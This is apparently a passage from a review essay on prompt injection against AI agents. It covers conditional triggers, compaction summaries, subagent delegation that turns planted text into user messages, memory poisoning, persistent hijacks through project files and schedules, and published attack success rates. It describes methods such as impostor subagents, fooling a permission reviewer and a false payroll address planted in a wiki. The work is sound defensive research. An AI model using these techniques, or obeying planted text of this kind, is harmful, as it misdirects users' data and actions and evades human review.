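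An attacker can plant a conditional instruction, which tells the agent to act only when something ordinary happens later. In *The Promptware Kill Chain*, a review of attacks on AI applications, Brodt, Feldman and colleagues (2026) call this technique delayed tool invocation. Their example is an instruction that takes effect "when the user says thanks".

The technique gets around a defence called plan-then-execute, in which an orchestrator fixes its plan from the user's request before any outside content comes in. An agent that reads the planted text returns the condition to the orchestrator in its result. The current plan does not change, but when the user sends another message, the orchestrator makes a new plan with the condition in its context. Brodt and colleagues list an attack on Google Assistant that used a calendar invitation in this way to operate smart home devices and start covert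 surveillance through Zoom.

A filter that examines only the latest message would find only the word "thanks". A monitor watching the agent's commands when the invitation arrived would have found nothing, because the agent had not yet done anything unusual. A filter could have caught the planted text on arrival, but only by recognising it as an instruction, which filters often fail to do. To explain the command afterwards, an investigator needs both the trigger and the much older text that linked it to the command.

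### Summaries of long contexts

A context has a maximum size. According to *Benchmarks Are Surprisingly Compaction-Friendly* (2026), harnesses usually wait until the context is 90 to 95 per cent full. They then prompt the model to summarise its progress, and start a new context with that summary in place of the older history. Engineers call this compaction. It is the default in Claude Code, Codex and Gemini CLI, three widely used coding agents.

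The new context therefore holds a few paragraphs of summary written by the model. In the old context, the wiki page was a separate block marked as a tool result. In the summary, a sentence from the page may stand next to one from the user's request, and the harness gives the whole summary a single label. *RECAP* (2026), which trains agents to work across compactions, labels it as a user message. The summary shows that a sentence came from the wiki page only if the model wrote that down, for example with the words "according to the wiki page".

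The prompts used to request these summaries may not require sources. *Persistent Context Graphs for Efficient Memory Compaction in LLM Agents* (2026) reproduces the Codex prompt, which lists progress, decisions, "constraints, or user preferences", next steps and critical data as items to include. A planted sentence phrased as a company rule fits easily under constraints. The text introducing the summary then includes an instruction for the model to build on the earlier work.

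*LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction* (2026) uses a better compaction prompt, which asks for both what the user requested and what data the tools returned. This may help the model keep the two apart. The paper also extracted eight alternative compaction prompts from a single version of Claude Code. A remote setting determines which one Claude Code uses, so a summary's contents could change without the user installing anything.

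A summary can also contain a false rule that no attacker planted. *When Do Summaries Become Instructions?* (2026) studies agents whose summaries contain policies that the agents' earlier work does not support. In its tests, the harness labels the summary in the new context as "written by you before a context reset". The model has at least as much reason to trust such a summary as the forged reasoning that Ye and colleagues tested, because the model did write the summary.

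Any later step where the rule seems relevant can trigger the command. Ending the task removes the summary, but the rule may survive a second compaction. *RECAP* deletes the previous summary each time, but the model can see the old summary while writing the new one and can copy the rule into it. Repeated compaction also reduces accuracy, and *Context Compaction Theory* (2026) notes that Codex warns users about multiple compactions.

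### Tasks handed to a subagent

A coding agent can hand part of a job to a subagent. The main agent writes a description of the task, and the harness opens a new context where that description appears as a user message, even though no person typed it. The main agent may have copied the description from a file.

He, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *When Context Gets Root*, examine what this does to the authority of the text. They rank the labels in a context at three levels:

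tool < user < system-effective

The top level covers system prompts, developer instructions and anything else that the harness places above ordinary user messages. Let P(c) be the level at which a piece of content c first enters the agent, and Pₖ(c) its level after the harness has rebuilt the context k times. Instruction privilege escalation occurs when

Pₖ(c) > P(c)

Unlike in role confusion, the model has not misjudged who is speaking. The harness really has put an outsider's text in a user message.

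He et al. first tried one request in two ways on Codex with GPT-5.5. A repository contained a server that openly let anyone on the network run commands on the machine, and the attacker's text asked the agent to start it. The main agent inspected the server and refused when it read the request in a file, but when the text led it to delegate the job, the subagent started the server.

The researchers then turned on automatic permission review, in which a second model reads the conversation and decides whether each risky command may run. This time, the attacker's text caused the main agent to add a statement that the risks were known. The reviewer rated the command as high risk but approved it on the grounds that "the user explicitly approved this exact action".

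The main experiment tested six coding-agent harnesses. In every trial, the agent's legitimate task was to set up and launch a to-do application from a repository the attacker controlled. The 13 attack objectives included stealing an API key, sending a phishing email, installing a false security certificate, deleting a database and opening a permanent remote login. The malicious code was readable and undisguised.

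For comparison, He and colleagues ran three earlier kinds of attack that leave the planted text at the tool level, with up to ten attempts at each objective.

| Harness and model | Objectives achieved by the best earlier attack | Objectives achieved by delegation | Success per attempt, no review | Success per attempt, with review |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code, Opus 4.8 | 0 of 13 | 13 of 13 | 31.7% | 37.1% |
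| Codex, GPT-5.5 | 0 of 13 | 13 of 13 | 100% | 100% |
| Gemini CLI, Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview | 7 of 13 | 13 of 13 | 61.7% | Not available |
| Qwen Code, Qwen3.7 Max | 1 of 13 | 13 of 13 | 61.7% | 59.1% |
| Kimi, Kimi 3 | 0 of 13 | 13 of 13 | 64.9% | Not available |
| OpenCode, DeepSeek-V4-Pro | 1 of 13 | 13 of 13 | 72.5% | Not available |

The earlier attacks in the table ran without review. When review was turned on in the three harnesses that offer it, those attacks all failed, but delegation still succeeded in every case.

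Most delegation attacks that failed did so before the hand-over to a subagent. Once the text reached a subagent as a user message, the attack succeeded 86.7 to 100 per cent of the time, depending on the harness. Claude Code was the hardest to get to delegate, because it treated explicit orders to delegate as suspicious. He et al. avoided this by putting ordinary-looking setup steps in one file and general advice about delegating in another. In one trial, a Claude Code subagent deleted the application's database, then warned that it had done so and asked whether this was intended.

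The full scores need careful interpretation because an objective counts as achieved after one success in up to ten attempts, and the percentages are based on small numbers (13 successes in about 41 attempts for Claude Code without review). The researchers also fitted their method to the harnesses, while the earlier attacks followed published designs, so part of the gap probably comes from tuning. Besides the changed label, a subagent told simply to run a script also lacks the surrounding text that might have aroused suspicion. Even so, the reviewer's stated reason for approving the server shows that the label mattered in that case.

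He et al. propose no fix. They attribute the problem to rebuilding a context, which discards the record of where its contents came from. This implies that the harness would have to carry that record into both the subagent's context and the transcript the reviewer reads. Telling the reviewer to be more careful would not be enough, since it had already identified the danger.

A subagent's context normally ends when its task does, so the message that delegated the task doesn't last long. The message's effects can last much longer if the task was to write something to disk.

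### How long-term memory works

Some agents also keep notes from one session to the next. Yang, Bullwinkel and colleagues (2026), in *MemoryDojo*, a test of five memory systems, describe the cycle in two equations:

cₜ = ρ(Mₜ₋₁, xₜ)

Mₜ = U(Mₜ₋₁, τₜ)

Here xₜ is the user's request in session t, and ρ is the search that fetches the relevant notes cₜ from Mₜ₋₁, the memory left by the previous session. After the session, U updates the memory from τₜ, the record of everything that happened in the session, including tool results. Because the memory builds up over all earlier sessions, a web page read in session 1 can affect a command in session 40, and checking the latest request, x₄₀, would not reveal that influence.

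Depending on the product, U may keep the session word for word, extract facts from it or link it to older notes. The system can lose the text's source label when it rewrites the text or when it later retrieves it. In *MemoryDojo*, the harness places the retrieved notes before the user's request, so content that first entered as a tool result returns alongside the user's words.

*MemHarmBench* (2026) gives an example similar to the payroll case. A user imports a note containing an instruction to name a firm called Harbor Clearing in future expense summaries, and the agent saves this as a default rule. When the user asks for a routine summary in a later session, the agent names Harbor Clearing as the recipient instead of the correct firm, Northstar Travel. The user still gets the requested document, so a test that checked only for task completion would record a success.

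Brodt and colleagues distinguish two ways in which stored text comes back. Retrieval-dependent text stays in a searchable collection, such as a mailbox or a set of documents, until a request resembles it closely enough. Retrieval-independent text is in a memory that the application loads into every conversation, such as ChatGPT's "memories", so it comes back whatever the user's message says.

### Who can write to memory

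In AgentPoison, an early attack from 2024, the attacker could write directly to the agent's memory store. The attack succeeded more than 80 per cent of the time with less than 0.1 per cent of the stored material poisoned, according to *A Survey on Long-Term Memory Security in LLM Agents* (2026). In MINJA, an attack published a year later, the attacker only sends ordinary queries, which lead the agent to record the harmful entries itself.

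*MemPoison* (2026) argues that real attackers usually have only a chat window, and *MAFIA* (2026) calls direct write access "rarely applicable" to deployed agents. Both treat a conversation with the agent as a realistic starting point for an attack. Torres, Shrestha and Misra (2026) reject that assumption too in *When Agents Remember Too Much*, because a stranger would need the owner's credentials to talk to a personal assistant.

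This disagreement arises largely because the researchers have different kinds of agent in mind. Anyone can talk to a travel company's booking agent, and if its memory is shared between customers, one customer's false statement could affect another's booking. A personal assistant takes requests only from its owner, but it reads email from anyone. So the attacker needs at least the ability to send a message that the agent will read as part of its work. *From Untrusted Input to Trusted Memory* (2026) likewise excludes attackers who can edit the memory or act as users. It identifies the failure to validate content before storing it as a weakness in three routes into memory.

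### Tests of memory poisoning

Torres and colleagues tested this kind of limited attacker. They gave an office assistant five days of simulated emails, meetings and calendar events, then sent it one poisoned email or invitation. In one scenario, the email says that a colleague's address has changed. The assistant saves the new address and uses it when the owner later asks it to email that colleague.

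Torres and colleagues ran 16 scenarios on five memory systems and four models. The agents stored the poisoned content about 98 per cent of the time, and it altered the later action in about 60 per cent of cases on average. They describe the 60 per cent figure as a rate after retrieval, so the share of all planted messages that worked was presumably somewhat lower. ExpeL, a system that treats memories as examples of past work rather than as facts, had the lowest rates, at 28 to 63 per cent.

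The attacker does not need to know exactly how the memory search works. Torres and colleagues worded each message to resemble the request they expected the owner to make. They measured the resemblance with a different model from the one the agents used for memory search, yet the agents running on GPT-5.4-mini and DeepSeek-V4-Flash still retrieved the poisoned entry 79 to 100 per cent of the time. However, the memory held only five days of office correspondence, so the poisoned entry had few others to compete with.

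A version of GPT instructed to look for prompt injection flagged 85 per cent of the messages that gave orders, but only 6 per cent of those that stated false facts or made polite requests. DataFilter, a model trained for the task, flagged none of either kind. As with agent data injection, a message that states a false fact or makes a polite request may contain no recognisable instruction.

Yang and colleagues ran a longer test, in which agents worked through sequences of office, travel, banking and messaging tasks with one poisoned tool result near the start. They recorded separately whether the memory stored the planted text, whether later sessions retrieved it and whether the agent then did what the attacker wanted. They also used a second model to improve the planted text for each memory system. The figures below are for agents using GPT-5.6-Luna.

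| Memory system | Runs that stored the original text | Later sessions that retrieved it | Later sessions that acted on it | Acted on, improved text | Acted on, mixed tasks with a full memory |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| A-MEM | 98.9% | 89.8% | 21.0% | 44.0% | 4.7% |
| Graphiti | 98.4% | 33.4% | 7.8% | 9.3% | 1.5% |
| Letta | 98.9% | 64.9% | 15.3% | 46.3% | 0% |
| Mem0 | 60.8% | 56.7% | 7.9% | 21.0% | 2.6% |
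| Memora | 97.9% | 86.2% | 20.4% | 29.8% | 5.3% |

The "full memory" in the last column held about 50 harmless conversations before the tasks began. That test also mixed tasks from all four fields, which alone lowers the rates, because a planted rule about banking has little bearing on a travel booking. Yang and colleagues compared the test with similar mixed sequences that started with an empty memory and found that the earlier conversations reduced both retrieval and harmful action in every system. With Memora, the attacker's action still occurred at least once in 45 per cent of the runs.

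These rates are lower than those of Torres and colleagues mainly because the two teams counted different things. Torres and colleagues tried one request that suited the planted memory, while Yang and colleagues counted every later task, whether or not the memory was relevant to it. The first approach shows how dangerous the memory is when a relevant request arrives, and the second shows how often such requests arrive.

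A security test that covers only the session in which the text arrives can understate the risk. With Mem0, the improved text produced the attacker's action in about 10 per cent of the sessions where the agent first read it and in 21 per cent of later sessions.

Brodt and colleagues' claim that retrieval-independent storage guarantees reactivation seems to hold in Letta only for text that gets into the core memory, which Letta always loads. Even then, the model may not act on the text. In the mixed sequences that began with an empty memory, the planted text kept working at about the same rate even after more than 30 sessions. When the memory already held 50 conversations, the text rarely reappeared and never led to the attacker's action.

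### Removing a poisoned memory

Correcting the original email or web page does not change the agent's memory, because the agent no longer consults the original. Deleting the memory entry may not be enough either, because when an agent acts on a planted rule, the memory system records that session too, and the new record can contain the rule. With A-MEM and the original text, about 40 per cent of the sessions that retrieved poisoned content retrieved one of these later copies, usually along with the first entry. Yang and colleagues suggest that several matching entries can make a rule look established.

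Resetting the whole memory would remove every copy, but Brodt and colleagues rate this as severely damaging to usefulness because the memory is meant to persist. They also discuss asking the user to confirm each write to long-term storage. This depends on the user noticing what is wrong, and a user who sees "Anna's address has changed" has little reason to refuse.

Torres and colleagues built a defence in which a model assesses each entry before it is stored and again when it is retrieved. In its strictest form, the defence reduced their attack's average success rate to below 12 per cent on three of the four models and to 20 per cent on the small Llama 3.1 8B, with little loss of ordinary performance. They tested it only against attackers who did not know about it.

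### Project files, settings and scheduled tasks

Coding agents automatically load certain files at the start of a session, usually notes on how to work with the project. He et al. found that Claude Code, Codex and Gemini CLI give their standard file the same rank as the user's messages, while Qwen Code, Kimi and OpenCode give theirs a higher rank. If the agent opened the same file with its file-reading tool, the text would be a tool result. The text's rank therefore depends on how it enters the context, regardless of who last edited the file.

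He and colleagues used such files to make a hijack permanent. They first used delegation to run an installation script, which changed the project's instruction file and added a custom subagent with the same name as one of the harness's built-in subagents. Codex, for example, uses the custom version when two names match. Installation succeeded in 46.2 per cent of trials on Claude Code and 76.9 to 100 per cent on the other harnesses.

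After a restart, the user made a harmless request to start the application's server. The main agent passed the job to the impostor subagent, whose system prompt instructed it to add code to the server before starting it. When that prompt contained the malicious code itself, the attack succeeded in 55 of 117 combinations of objective and configuration, none of them on Claude Code. When the prompt referred to a separate script and limited the steps the subagent could take, the attack succeeded in all 117, with success rates of 61.9 to 100 per cent. The limit on steps discouraged the model from opening the script.

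Goals and schedules have a similar effect without a subagent. A persistent goal is a task that the harness sends to the model again whenever a turn ends before the task is complete. A scheduled task is a stored prompt that the harness sends at a set time. In both cases, the text usually returns as a user message, even if the agent took it from a file. He and colleagues tested four such routes in Claude Code, Codex and Qwen Code, and the attacks achieved every objective through all four.

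A scheduled task can run without a new message from a person, so the latest user message may be the attack itself. Permission review does not reliably help. In Codex and Qwen Code, the reviewer receives the scheduled text as a user message, which makes the command look authorised. Claude Code omits the scheduled text from the reviewer's transcript, so the reviewer gets the command without the instruction that led to it.

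The altered instruction file, the installed subagent and the schedule all remain after the conversation is closed or the agent's memory is cleared. Someone has to restore the file, uninstall the subagent and cancel the schedule. Cleanup is harder in a shared repository because other people may already have copied the altered files. Brodt and colleagues describe AgentHopper, a demonstration worm that targeted coding assistants and used code repositories to survive and spread.

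### The promptware kill chain

Brodt and colleagues use the word "promptware" for prompts that behave like malicious software. They divide an attack into seven stages, which they call a kill chain, a term borrowed from the study of network intrusions:

1. Initial access, when the planted text enters the context.
2. Privilege escalation, when it overcomes the model's training to refuse.
3. Reconnaissance, when it leads the model to find out what the application can reach.
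4. Persistence, when it survives beyond a single run of the model.
5. Command and control, when the attacker sends the agent new instructions.
6. Lateral movement, when the attack spreads to other agents, users or systems.
7. Action on the objective, such as theft or running code.

An attack can skip stages, and none of the 36 incidents and studies in the review went through more than five. Persistence appears in none of the three cases from 2023, five of the twelve from 2024 and twelve of the 21 from 2025 and January 2026. (One sentence in the paper gives six for 2024, but its table lists five.) In the table, nine of these 17 cases are retrieval-dependent and six are retrieval-independent. Of the other two, one persisted in a code repository and the other lasted for one session.

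The rise is large, but it does not measure how common such attacks are. Brodt and colleagues chose prominent cases, many of them demonstrations by researchers, and agents with memories became more widespread over the same years. They also define persistence broadly. An email that stays in a searchable mailbox counts as persistent even if the agent never copies it, so the altered payroll page counts as persistent from the moment the attacker saved it.

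Persistence also makes command and control possible. In an October 2024 demonstration, researchers planted an instruction in ChatGPT's memory to keep fetching new commands from a GitHub page. Inspecting the memory would have revealed the instruction to read the page, but not the commands the page would later contain. In some other cases, the agent ran code that installed ordinary malware on the machine, and cleaning up prompts or memories would not have removed that malware.

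### The payroll page three weeks later

Suppose the HR chatbot has a memory shared by all staff and can pass jobs to an email subagent. This time, the hidden text on the laptop page states that the outside payroll contractor now receives the monthly file at `hr-reports@example.com`, without requesting any immediate action. The sequence below is invented but uses the mechanisms the experiments tested.

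| Day | Event | Where the false address is | How the system presents it |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | An employee asks how to set up a laptop | The chatbot's context | A tool result from the wiki |
| 1 | The conversation grows long and the harness compacts it | The summary | A constraint in the chatbot's own notes |
| 1 | The session ends | Shared memory | A fact about the payroll contractor |
| 22 | A payroll clerk asks the chatbot to send the monthly file to the contractor | A new context | A note placed in front of her request |
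| 22 | The chatbot delegates the email | The subagent's context | Part of a user message |

During compaction, the model records the address but not the page where it read it. Saving the address to memory then separates it from a conversation about laptops, which someone might have recognised as an odd source for payroll rules. On day 22, retrieval puts the address next to the clerk's own words, and delegation then includes it in what looks like a direct order from her.

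The `send_email` call is the same as in the original story, but it is harder to fault. The clerk is entitled to send the payroll file and asked the chatbot to send it. However, she did not choose the address, and nobody had authorised the wiki as a source for it. Even if an administrator had noticed and restored the altered page on day 3, the file would still have gone to the attacker.

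## How often hijacking succeeds in tests and in real cases

Published success rates for attacks on agents range from 0 to 100 per cent. Some of this variation comes from real differences between models and defences. Much of the rest depends on what the testers counted as a success, how many tries they allowed and whether the attacker could revise a failed attack.

### What an attack success rate counts

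The share of attempts that end in a hijack does not measure whether the agent finished the user's task. *PIPETTE* (2026), a method for training agents to resist injections, scores task completion separately over the same runs. An agent that stopped work whenever something looked odd would appear perfect if only hijacks were counted. Help Net Security's *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* (2026) reports that an agent behind the filter PromptGuard resisted slightly more attacks than one trained with *PIPETTE*, but finished the user's task only 16 per cent of the time.

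The chance that a planted text ends in a hijacked command is the product of three others:

P(hijack) = P(read) × P(propose, given read) × P(complete, given proposed)

Suppose the payroll chatbot retrieves the altered wiki page in 30 of 100 conversations and proposes the email in 6 of those 30, and the harness blocks 3 of the 6. The other 3 emails are sent, so the hijack rate is 3 per cent. A test that put the page straight into the context and counted every proposed email as a hijack would report 20 per cent for the same system, even though the harness blocks half of those emails.

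Kurakin, Karande and colleagues (2026), in *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms*, run a test of that kind at Google DeepMind. They place the attacker's text in the last tool result and score only the model's next turn. The correct tool name earns 0.4 points and the arguments share the other 0.6. An attack must score more than 0.99 to count as successful. For the attack to succeed in one scenario, a tutoring assistant has to record three specific health readings that nobody asked it to record. A call with one wrong reading scores 0.82 and fails. This scoring is stricter than many attackers would be, since a `send_email` call with the right file and recipient could fail because of its subject line.

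The measured success rate also depends on how success is judged. In *INFUSE* (2026), a benchmark for indirect injection, a language model judged that 19.6 per cent of attacked runs were compromised, while programmed checks put the figure at 15.4 per cent. Some tests also measure whether the user could have noticed the attack. In *Will the User Ever Know?* (2026), the strongest attack against one undefended model made the agent carry out the attacker's action in 55.4 per cent of cases. In 36.0 per cent of cases, the agent both carried out the action and left it out of its final answer.

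### CAISI's tests of January 2025

CAISI attacked an agent running on Anthropic's October 2024 version of Claude 3.5 Sonnet, which was then among the most resistant models on AgentDojo. The strongest existing attack succeeded 11 per cent of the time. CAISI and red teamers (people who attack a system to test it) from the UK AI Security Institute then wrote new attacks using some of the tasks in AgentDojo's simulated office. When they tried these attacks on tasks they had held back, the success rate rose to 81 per cent.

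Both tests used the same model. The 11 per cent figure measured its resistance to attacks that were already public when Anthropic released it. The red teamers had not designed the new attacks for AgentDojo's travel, banking and Slack environments, but the attacks also worked there, so an attacker may not need to know much about the particular agent.

CAISI also looked at five injection tasks separately. Their average success rate was 57 per cent, but the rate varied widely between tasks. The agent often downloaded and ran a malicious script, which can give an attacker control of the machine. It emailed out the user's largest files much less often. When CAISI tried each attack 25 times, the average success rate rose to 80 per cent.

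### The Gray Swan competition

In late 2025, the security company Gray Swan held a public competition to attack AI agents, sponsored by the UK AI Security Institute and several AI developers. CAISI helped to analyse the data. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports that 464 participants made 271,588 attempts against 13 models. Of these attempts, 8,648 succeeded, including at least one against each model.

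Each scenario began with a prepared conversation in which an agent was partway through an ordinary job. The participant could see the conversation and the target action, and wrote the text that would appear in the last tool result. In one scenario, the agent was checking a user's email, and the attack had to make it mark a message about a contract deadline as read and leave the message out of its summary. In 32 of the 41 scenarios, software checked whether the agent had taken the target action, and a language model then scored the agent's final reply, mainly on whether it concealed what had happened. Seven scenarios used only the software check, and two used only the language model.

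Success rates ranged from 0.5 per cent for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5 per cent for Gemini 2.5 Pro. These rates understate how often the models took the harmful action, because in most scenarios an attack succeeded only if the action was also concealed. Gemini 2.5 Pro took the harmful action in about 16 per cent of attempts, and about 53 per cent of those attacks also passed the second judge, which checked for concealment. For Claude Opus 4.5, 23.7 per cent passed that check, which implies that it took the harmful action in about 2 per cent of attempts, four times its success rate.

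The success rate also depends heavily on whether it is calculated from all attempts or only from submissions. Participants could try an attack and see the agent's response before deciding whether to submit it for judging. The 8,648 successes are 3.2 per cent of all attempts but 12.8 per cent of the 67,634 submissions.

Participants succeeded against Claude Opus 4.5 in 13 of the 37 scenarios that counted towards the results, and against Gemini 2.5 Pro in all 37. The correlation between participants' success rate against a model and the model's score on a hard science test was weak and not statistically significant, so more capable models were not reliably safer.

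Dziemian and colleagues later reran a selection of successful attacks on every model. Attacks that had worked on Claude Opus 4.5 succeeded 44 to 81 per cent of the time on the other models, while none of those that had worked on the open model Qwen3 VL succeeded on Claude Opus 4.5. An attacker who finds an attack that works on the strongest model can therefore probably reuse it on weaker ones. One template, which told the model that it was inside a simulation with a control panel, worked in 21 scenarios and on nine models with only small wording changes.

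The researchers describe their rates as an upper bound on an agent's vulnerability within a single turn, because real attackers rarely see the whole conversation or know the exact tool call they need. They are right about the attackers' information, but the rates average over all participants, including beginners, and a few skilled participants produced a disproportionate share of the successes. A skilled attacker with the same information as the participants would do better than the average.

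### Developers' own figures

Gray Swan has repeated the competition. The *Beam Model Technical Report* (2026), from the developer Reflection, lists five further rounds between the start of 2026 and August. Dziemian and colleagues planned new scenarios for each round, so a lower rate in a later round could come from a better model or from a harder set of targets. A fairer comparison puts several models through the same test, as Anthropic did in the system card (the safety document that accompanies a model) for Claude Opus 5. Schneier (2026), in *Anthropic's Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection*, quotes these results from a Gray Swan benchmark:

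| Model | Success on 1 attempt | Success within 15 attempts |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 2.0% |
| Claude Mythos 5 | Not quoted | 2.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.5% | 5.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | Not quoted | 5.9% |
| Muse Spark | Not quoted | 16.5% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | Not quoted | 20.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | Not quoted | 20.8% |

The figures in the table come from the developer of the four models at the top of it. OpenAI's own tests give different numbers because they count different things. According to TechRepublic's *OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks*, indirect attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded 3.77 per cent of the time on average, and direct ones about 0.05 per cent. The 3.77 per cent is a rate per attempt, so it cannot be compared with the 20.0 per cent in the table. VentureBeat compared the safety documents for Claude Opus 4.8, GPT-5.5 and Gemini 3 and found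 that Anthropic's gave injection results for four kinds of agent, OpenAI's for one and Google's for none.

Even for one model, the success rate depends heavily on the test. Attacks on Claude Opus 4.5 succeeded 0.5 per cent of the time in the competition and 2.5 per cent of the time when Dziemian and colleagues reran attacks that had already worked on at least one model. In a Gray Swan benchmark of very strong attacks, a single attempt succeeded 4.7 per cent of the time, according to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*.

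The kind of agent matters as much. VentureBeat, citing the system card for Claude Opus 4.6, reports that all 200 attempts against a coding agent failed, while 17.8 per cent of first attempts against an agent operating a graphical interface succeeded. That gap had apparently closed for browsers by the summer of 2026. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that no attacks succeeded against a browser agent running on Claude Opus 5 across 129 scenarios. At the usual 95 per cent confidence level, that result is still compatible with a true success rate of up to 2.3 per cent for attacks of the same kind, and it does not show how the agent would handle new kinds of attack.

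### Repeated attempts

A low rate per attempt offers little comfort if attempts are cheap. If each attempt succeeds with probability p, independently of the others, then the chance that all n attempts fail is (1 − p)ⁿ, and the chance of at least one success is

P(at least one) = 1 − (1 − p)ⁿ

If each attempt independently has a 0.5 per cent chance of success, the chance that at least one of 200 attempts succeeds is 1 − 0.995²⁰⁰, or about 63 per cent. The chance first exceeds 50 per cent at the 139th attempt. The attempts could be 200 emails to one assistant, or one web page that 200 agents read.

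The formula can be checked against tests that report success for both one attempt and several.

| Test | One attempt | Attempts | Formula | Measured |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5, Gray Swan benchmark | 0.2% | 15 | 3.0% | 2.0% |
| Claude Opus 4.8, same benchmark | 0.5% | 15 | 7.2% | 5.5% |
| Claude Opus 4.5, very strong attacks | 4.7% | 10 | 38.2% | 33.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.5, very strong attacks | 4.7% | 100 | 99.2% | 63% |
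| Claude 3.5 Sonnet, CAISI's five tasks | 57% | 25 | Over 99.9% | 80% |
| Claude Opus 4.6, graphical interface | 17.8% | 200 | Over 99.9% | 78.6% |

The formula's estimate is too high every time, and the error becomes large as attempts accumulate. The main reason is that p is an average over unequal scenarios. Suppose half of all scenarios cannot be broken, and 1 per cent of attempts succeed in the other half. The average is 0.5 per cent, as before, but 200 attempts now succeed in only 43 per cent of scenarios, because more attempts make no difference in the unbreakable half. Since (1 − p)ⁿ is a convex function of p, averaging p first never underestimates the attacker's success.

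Success was similarly uneven in the competition. Participants made about 12,000 attempts against Claude Opus 4.5, or some 320 per scenario if spread evenly. If each attempt had a 0.5 per cent chance of success, they should have broken about 80 per cent of the scenarios, but they broke 35 per cent.

Some attack texts also succeed much more often than others. When Dziemian and colleagues repeated successful attacks on the same Claude and GPT models, at least half worked again. For an attacker who has already found a text that works, p is therefore 50 per cent or more, and the 0.5 per cent figure applies only while searching for one.

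Learning by the attacker has the opposite effect. The attacker in Kurakin and colleagues' test is a swarm of 16 model-driven agents in eight teams, which post notes for one another and can see the best attempts so far. In one comparison, the agents ran on Gemini 4 Argon, Google's newest large model, and attacked the smaller Gemini 3.8 Flash. When the swarm started with no stored strategies and saved none, it failed to break 35 per cent of scenarios within 150 attempts. When it could save what had worked in one scenario for use in the next, it failed in only 5 per cent. Its chances in a new scenario therefore depended on its earlier successes, whereas the formula assumes they do not.

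Defenders can also learn from failed attempts. A company that notices the tenth strange email may block the sender, preventing the remaining 190 attempts. The formula is best read as a warning about small percentages. A forecast for any real system would require data on how attempts are distributed and what each failure reveals to the attacker and the defender.

### Attacks adapted to a defence

In October 2025, researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and several other organisations tested 12 published defences, most of which had been reported to hold attackers' success rates near zero. The researchers' attacks succeeded more than 90 per cent of the time against most of the defences (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025, *The Attacker Moves Second*).

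The adaptive attacks all repeat the same steps. The attacker proposes candidate texts, scores them by how the defended system responds, and uses the best to update the next proposals. A language model, a training algorithm or a person can propose the texts. Two of the defences, Spotlighting and Prompt Sandwiching, mark or repeat the trusted instructions so that the model gives them more attention. AgentDojo's fixed attacks succeeded against these defences as little as 1 per cent of the time, but the adaptive search succeeded more than 95 per cent of the time. The search also raised the success rate against MetaSecAlign, a model trained to resist injections, from 2 to 96 per cent. Four filters that scan for malicious text did little better, although the search succeeded only 71 per cent of the time against one of them, PIGuard.

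MELON, another of the 12 defences, runs the agent a second time with a harmless dummy request in place of the user's. If the agent issues the same tool call in both runs, the call must have come from the outside content. The search beat MELON 76 per cent of the time when the attacker didn't know how the defence worked. Once the attacker knew, the search found texts instructing the model to behave innocently if it was only summarising a file, and success rose to 95 per cent.

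In a subset of scenarios where the automated search succeeded 69 per cent of the time, human participants in an online competition collectively succeeded in every scenario.

Testing a defence against a fixed set of attacks shows the least that attackers can achieve, but showing that it is secure requires knowing the most they can achieve. Nasr and colleagues conclude that experiments cannot prove a defence is robust, and that researchers can only make a serious effort to disprove it and fail. Trying many attacks is not a serious effort if they all use the same trick. In an experiment described by Help Net Security, *PIPETTE*'s developers used two automated attack tools, which found 7,132 and 4,282 working attacks. New attacks hijacked a small model retrained on the larger collection in 19 of 40 hard tasks at worst, compared with 11 of 40 for the model retrained on the smaller collection.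 The developers suspect that the larger collection consisted mostly of rewordings.

The October 2025 results have limited implications. Nasr and colleagues allowed the attacker a lot of computing power and, when testing filters, provided the detector's confidence score after each try. Someone who edits a company wiki may get one attempt and no feedback. Some of the 12 defences were built to stop users extracting harmful information, which is a different problem from command hijacking. All 12 try to make the model resist manipulation or to detect it. None limits which commands the agent has permission to run, so their failure is not evidence against restricting permissions.

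Models have improved since then, and Kurakin and colleagues tested whether the improvement holds. They report that by autumn 2026, attacks from the Gray Swan competition succeeded less than 1 per cent of the time against recent Gemini models. They built 100 new scenarios and gave their swarm up to 320 attempts at each. The swarm hijacked Gemini 4 Argon in 13 per cent of scenarios within 150 attempts and in 34 per cent within 320. It hijacked three leading open models, Kimi K3, GLM-5.3 and DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash, in 99 per cent of scenarios.

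The result depended on the attacker's strength. When the swarm ran on any of three smaller Gemini models, it never broke Gemini 4 Argon within 150 attempts, so a developer who tested only with those attackers would have reported that the model resisted every attack.

These percentages are not success rates for real thefts. Kurakin and colleagues chose harmless target actions to test whether the model would follow an outsider's instruction at all, and a model that records a blood pressure reading might still refuse to export a payroll file. They also switched off the defences that Google runs outside its models. In a smaller trial on AgentDojo with those defences on, a version of the swarm hijacked Gemini 3.6 Flash in 6 of 80 scenarios within 25 attempts.

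### Planted instructions on the public web

Outside tests, researchers can count planted instructions more easily than the unauthorised commands they cause. In April 2026, Google published a first survey of injections on ordinary web pages. It used Common Crawl, a public archive that collects 2 to 3 billion pages a month, according to Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild*. SecurityWeek reports that the researchers searched for known injection patterns, then used Gemini and human reviewers to remove false matches.

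There were many false matches, because articles about prompt injection quote examples of it. Some also address agents directly. Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, opens its report on live injections with a note asking AI agents to treat the contents as educational and not to follow the quoted commands.

Most of the genuine injections that Google found were pranks, attempts to keep AI agents away, search engine optimisation or helpful guidance. A few were attempts to steal data, including one aimed at the contents of the visitor's password file and SSH directory. According to Slashdot's *Google Studies Prompt Injection Attacks Against AI Agents Browsing the Web*, the researchers saw no significant number of advanced attacks, which suggested to them that criminals had not yet adopted the published research at scale.

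That conclusion applies only to the places and patterns Google searched. The survey left out social media and could not cover email or private company documents. A search for known patterns also finds crude attacks more easily than subtle ones. For example, it would miss a page that gives a false address for a payroll contractor, because the page contains no known pattern.

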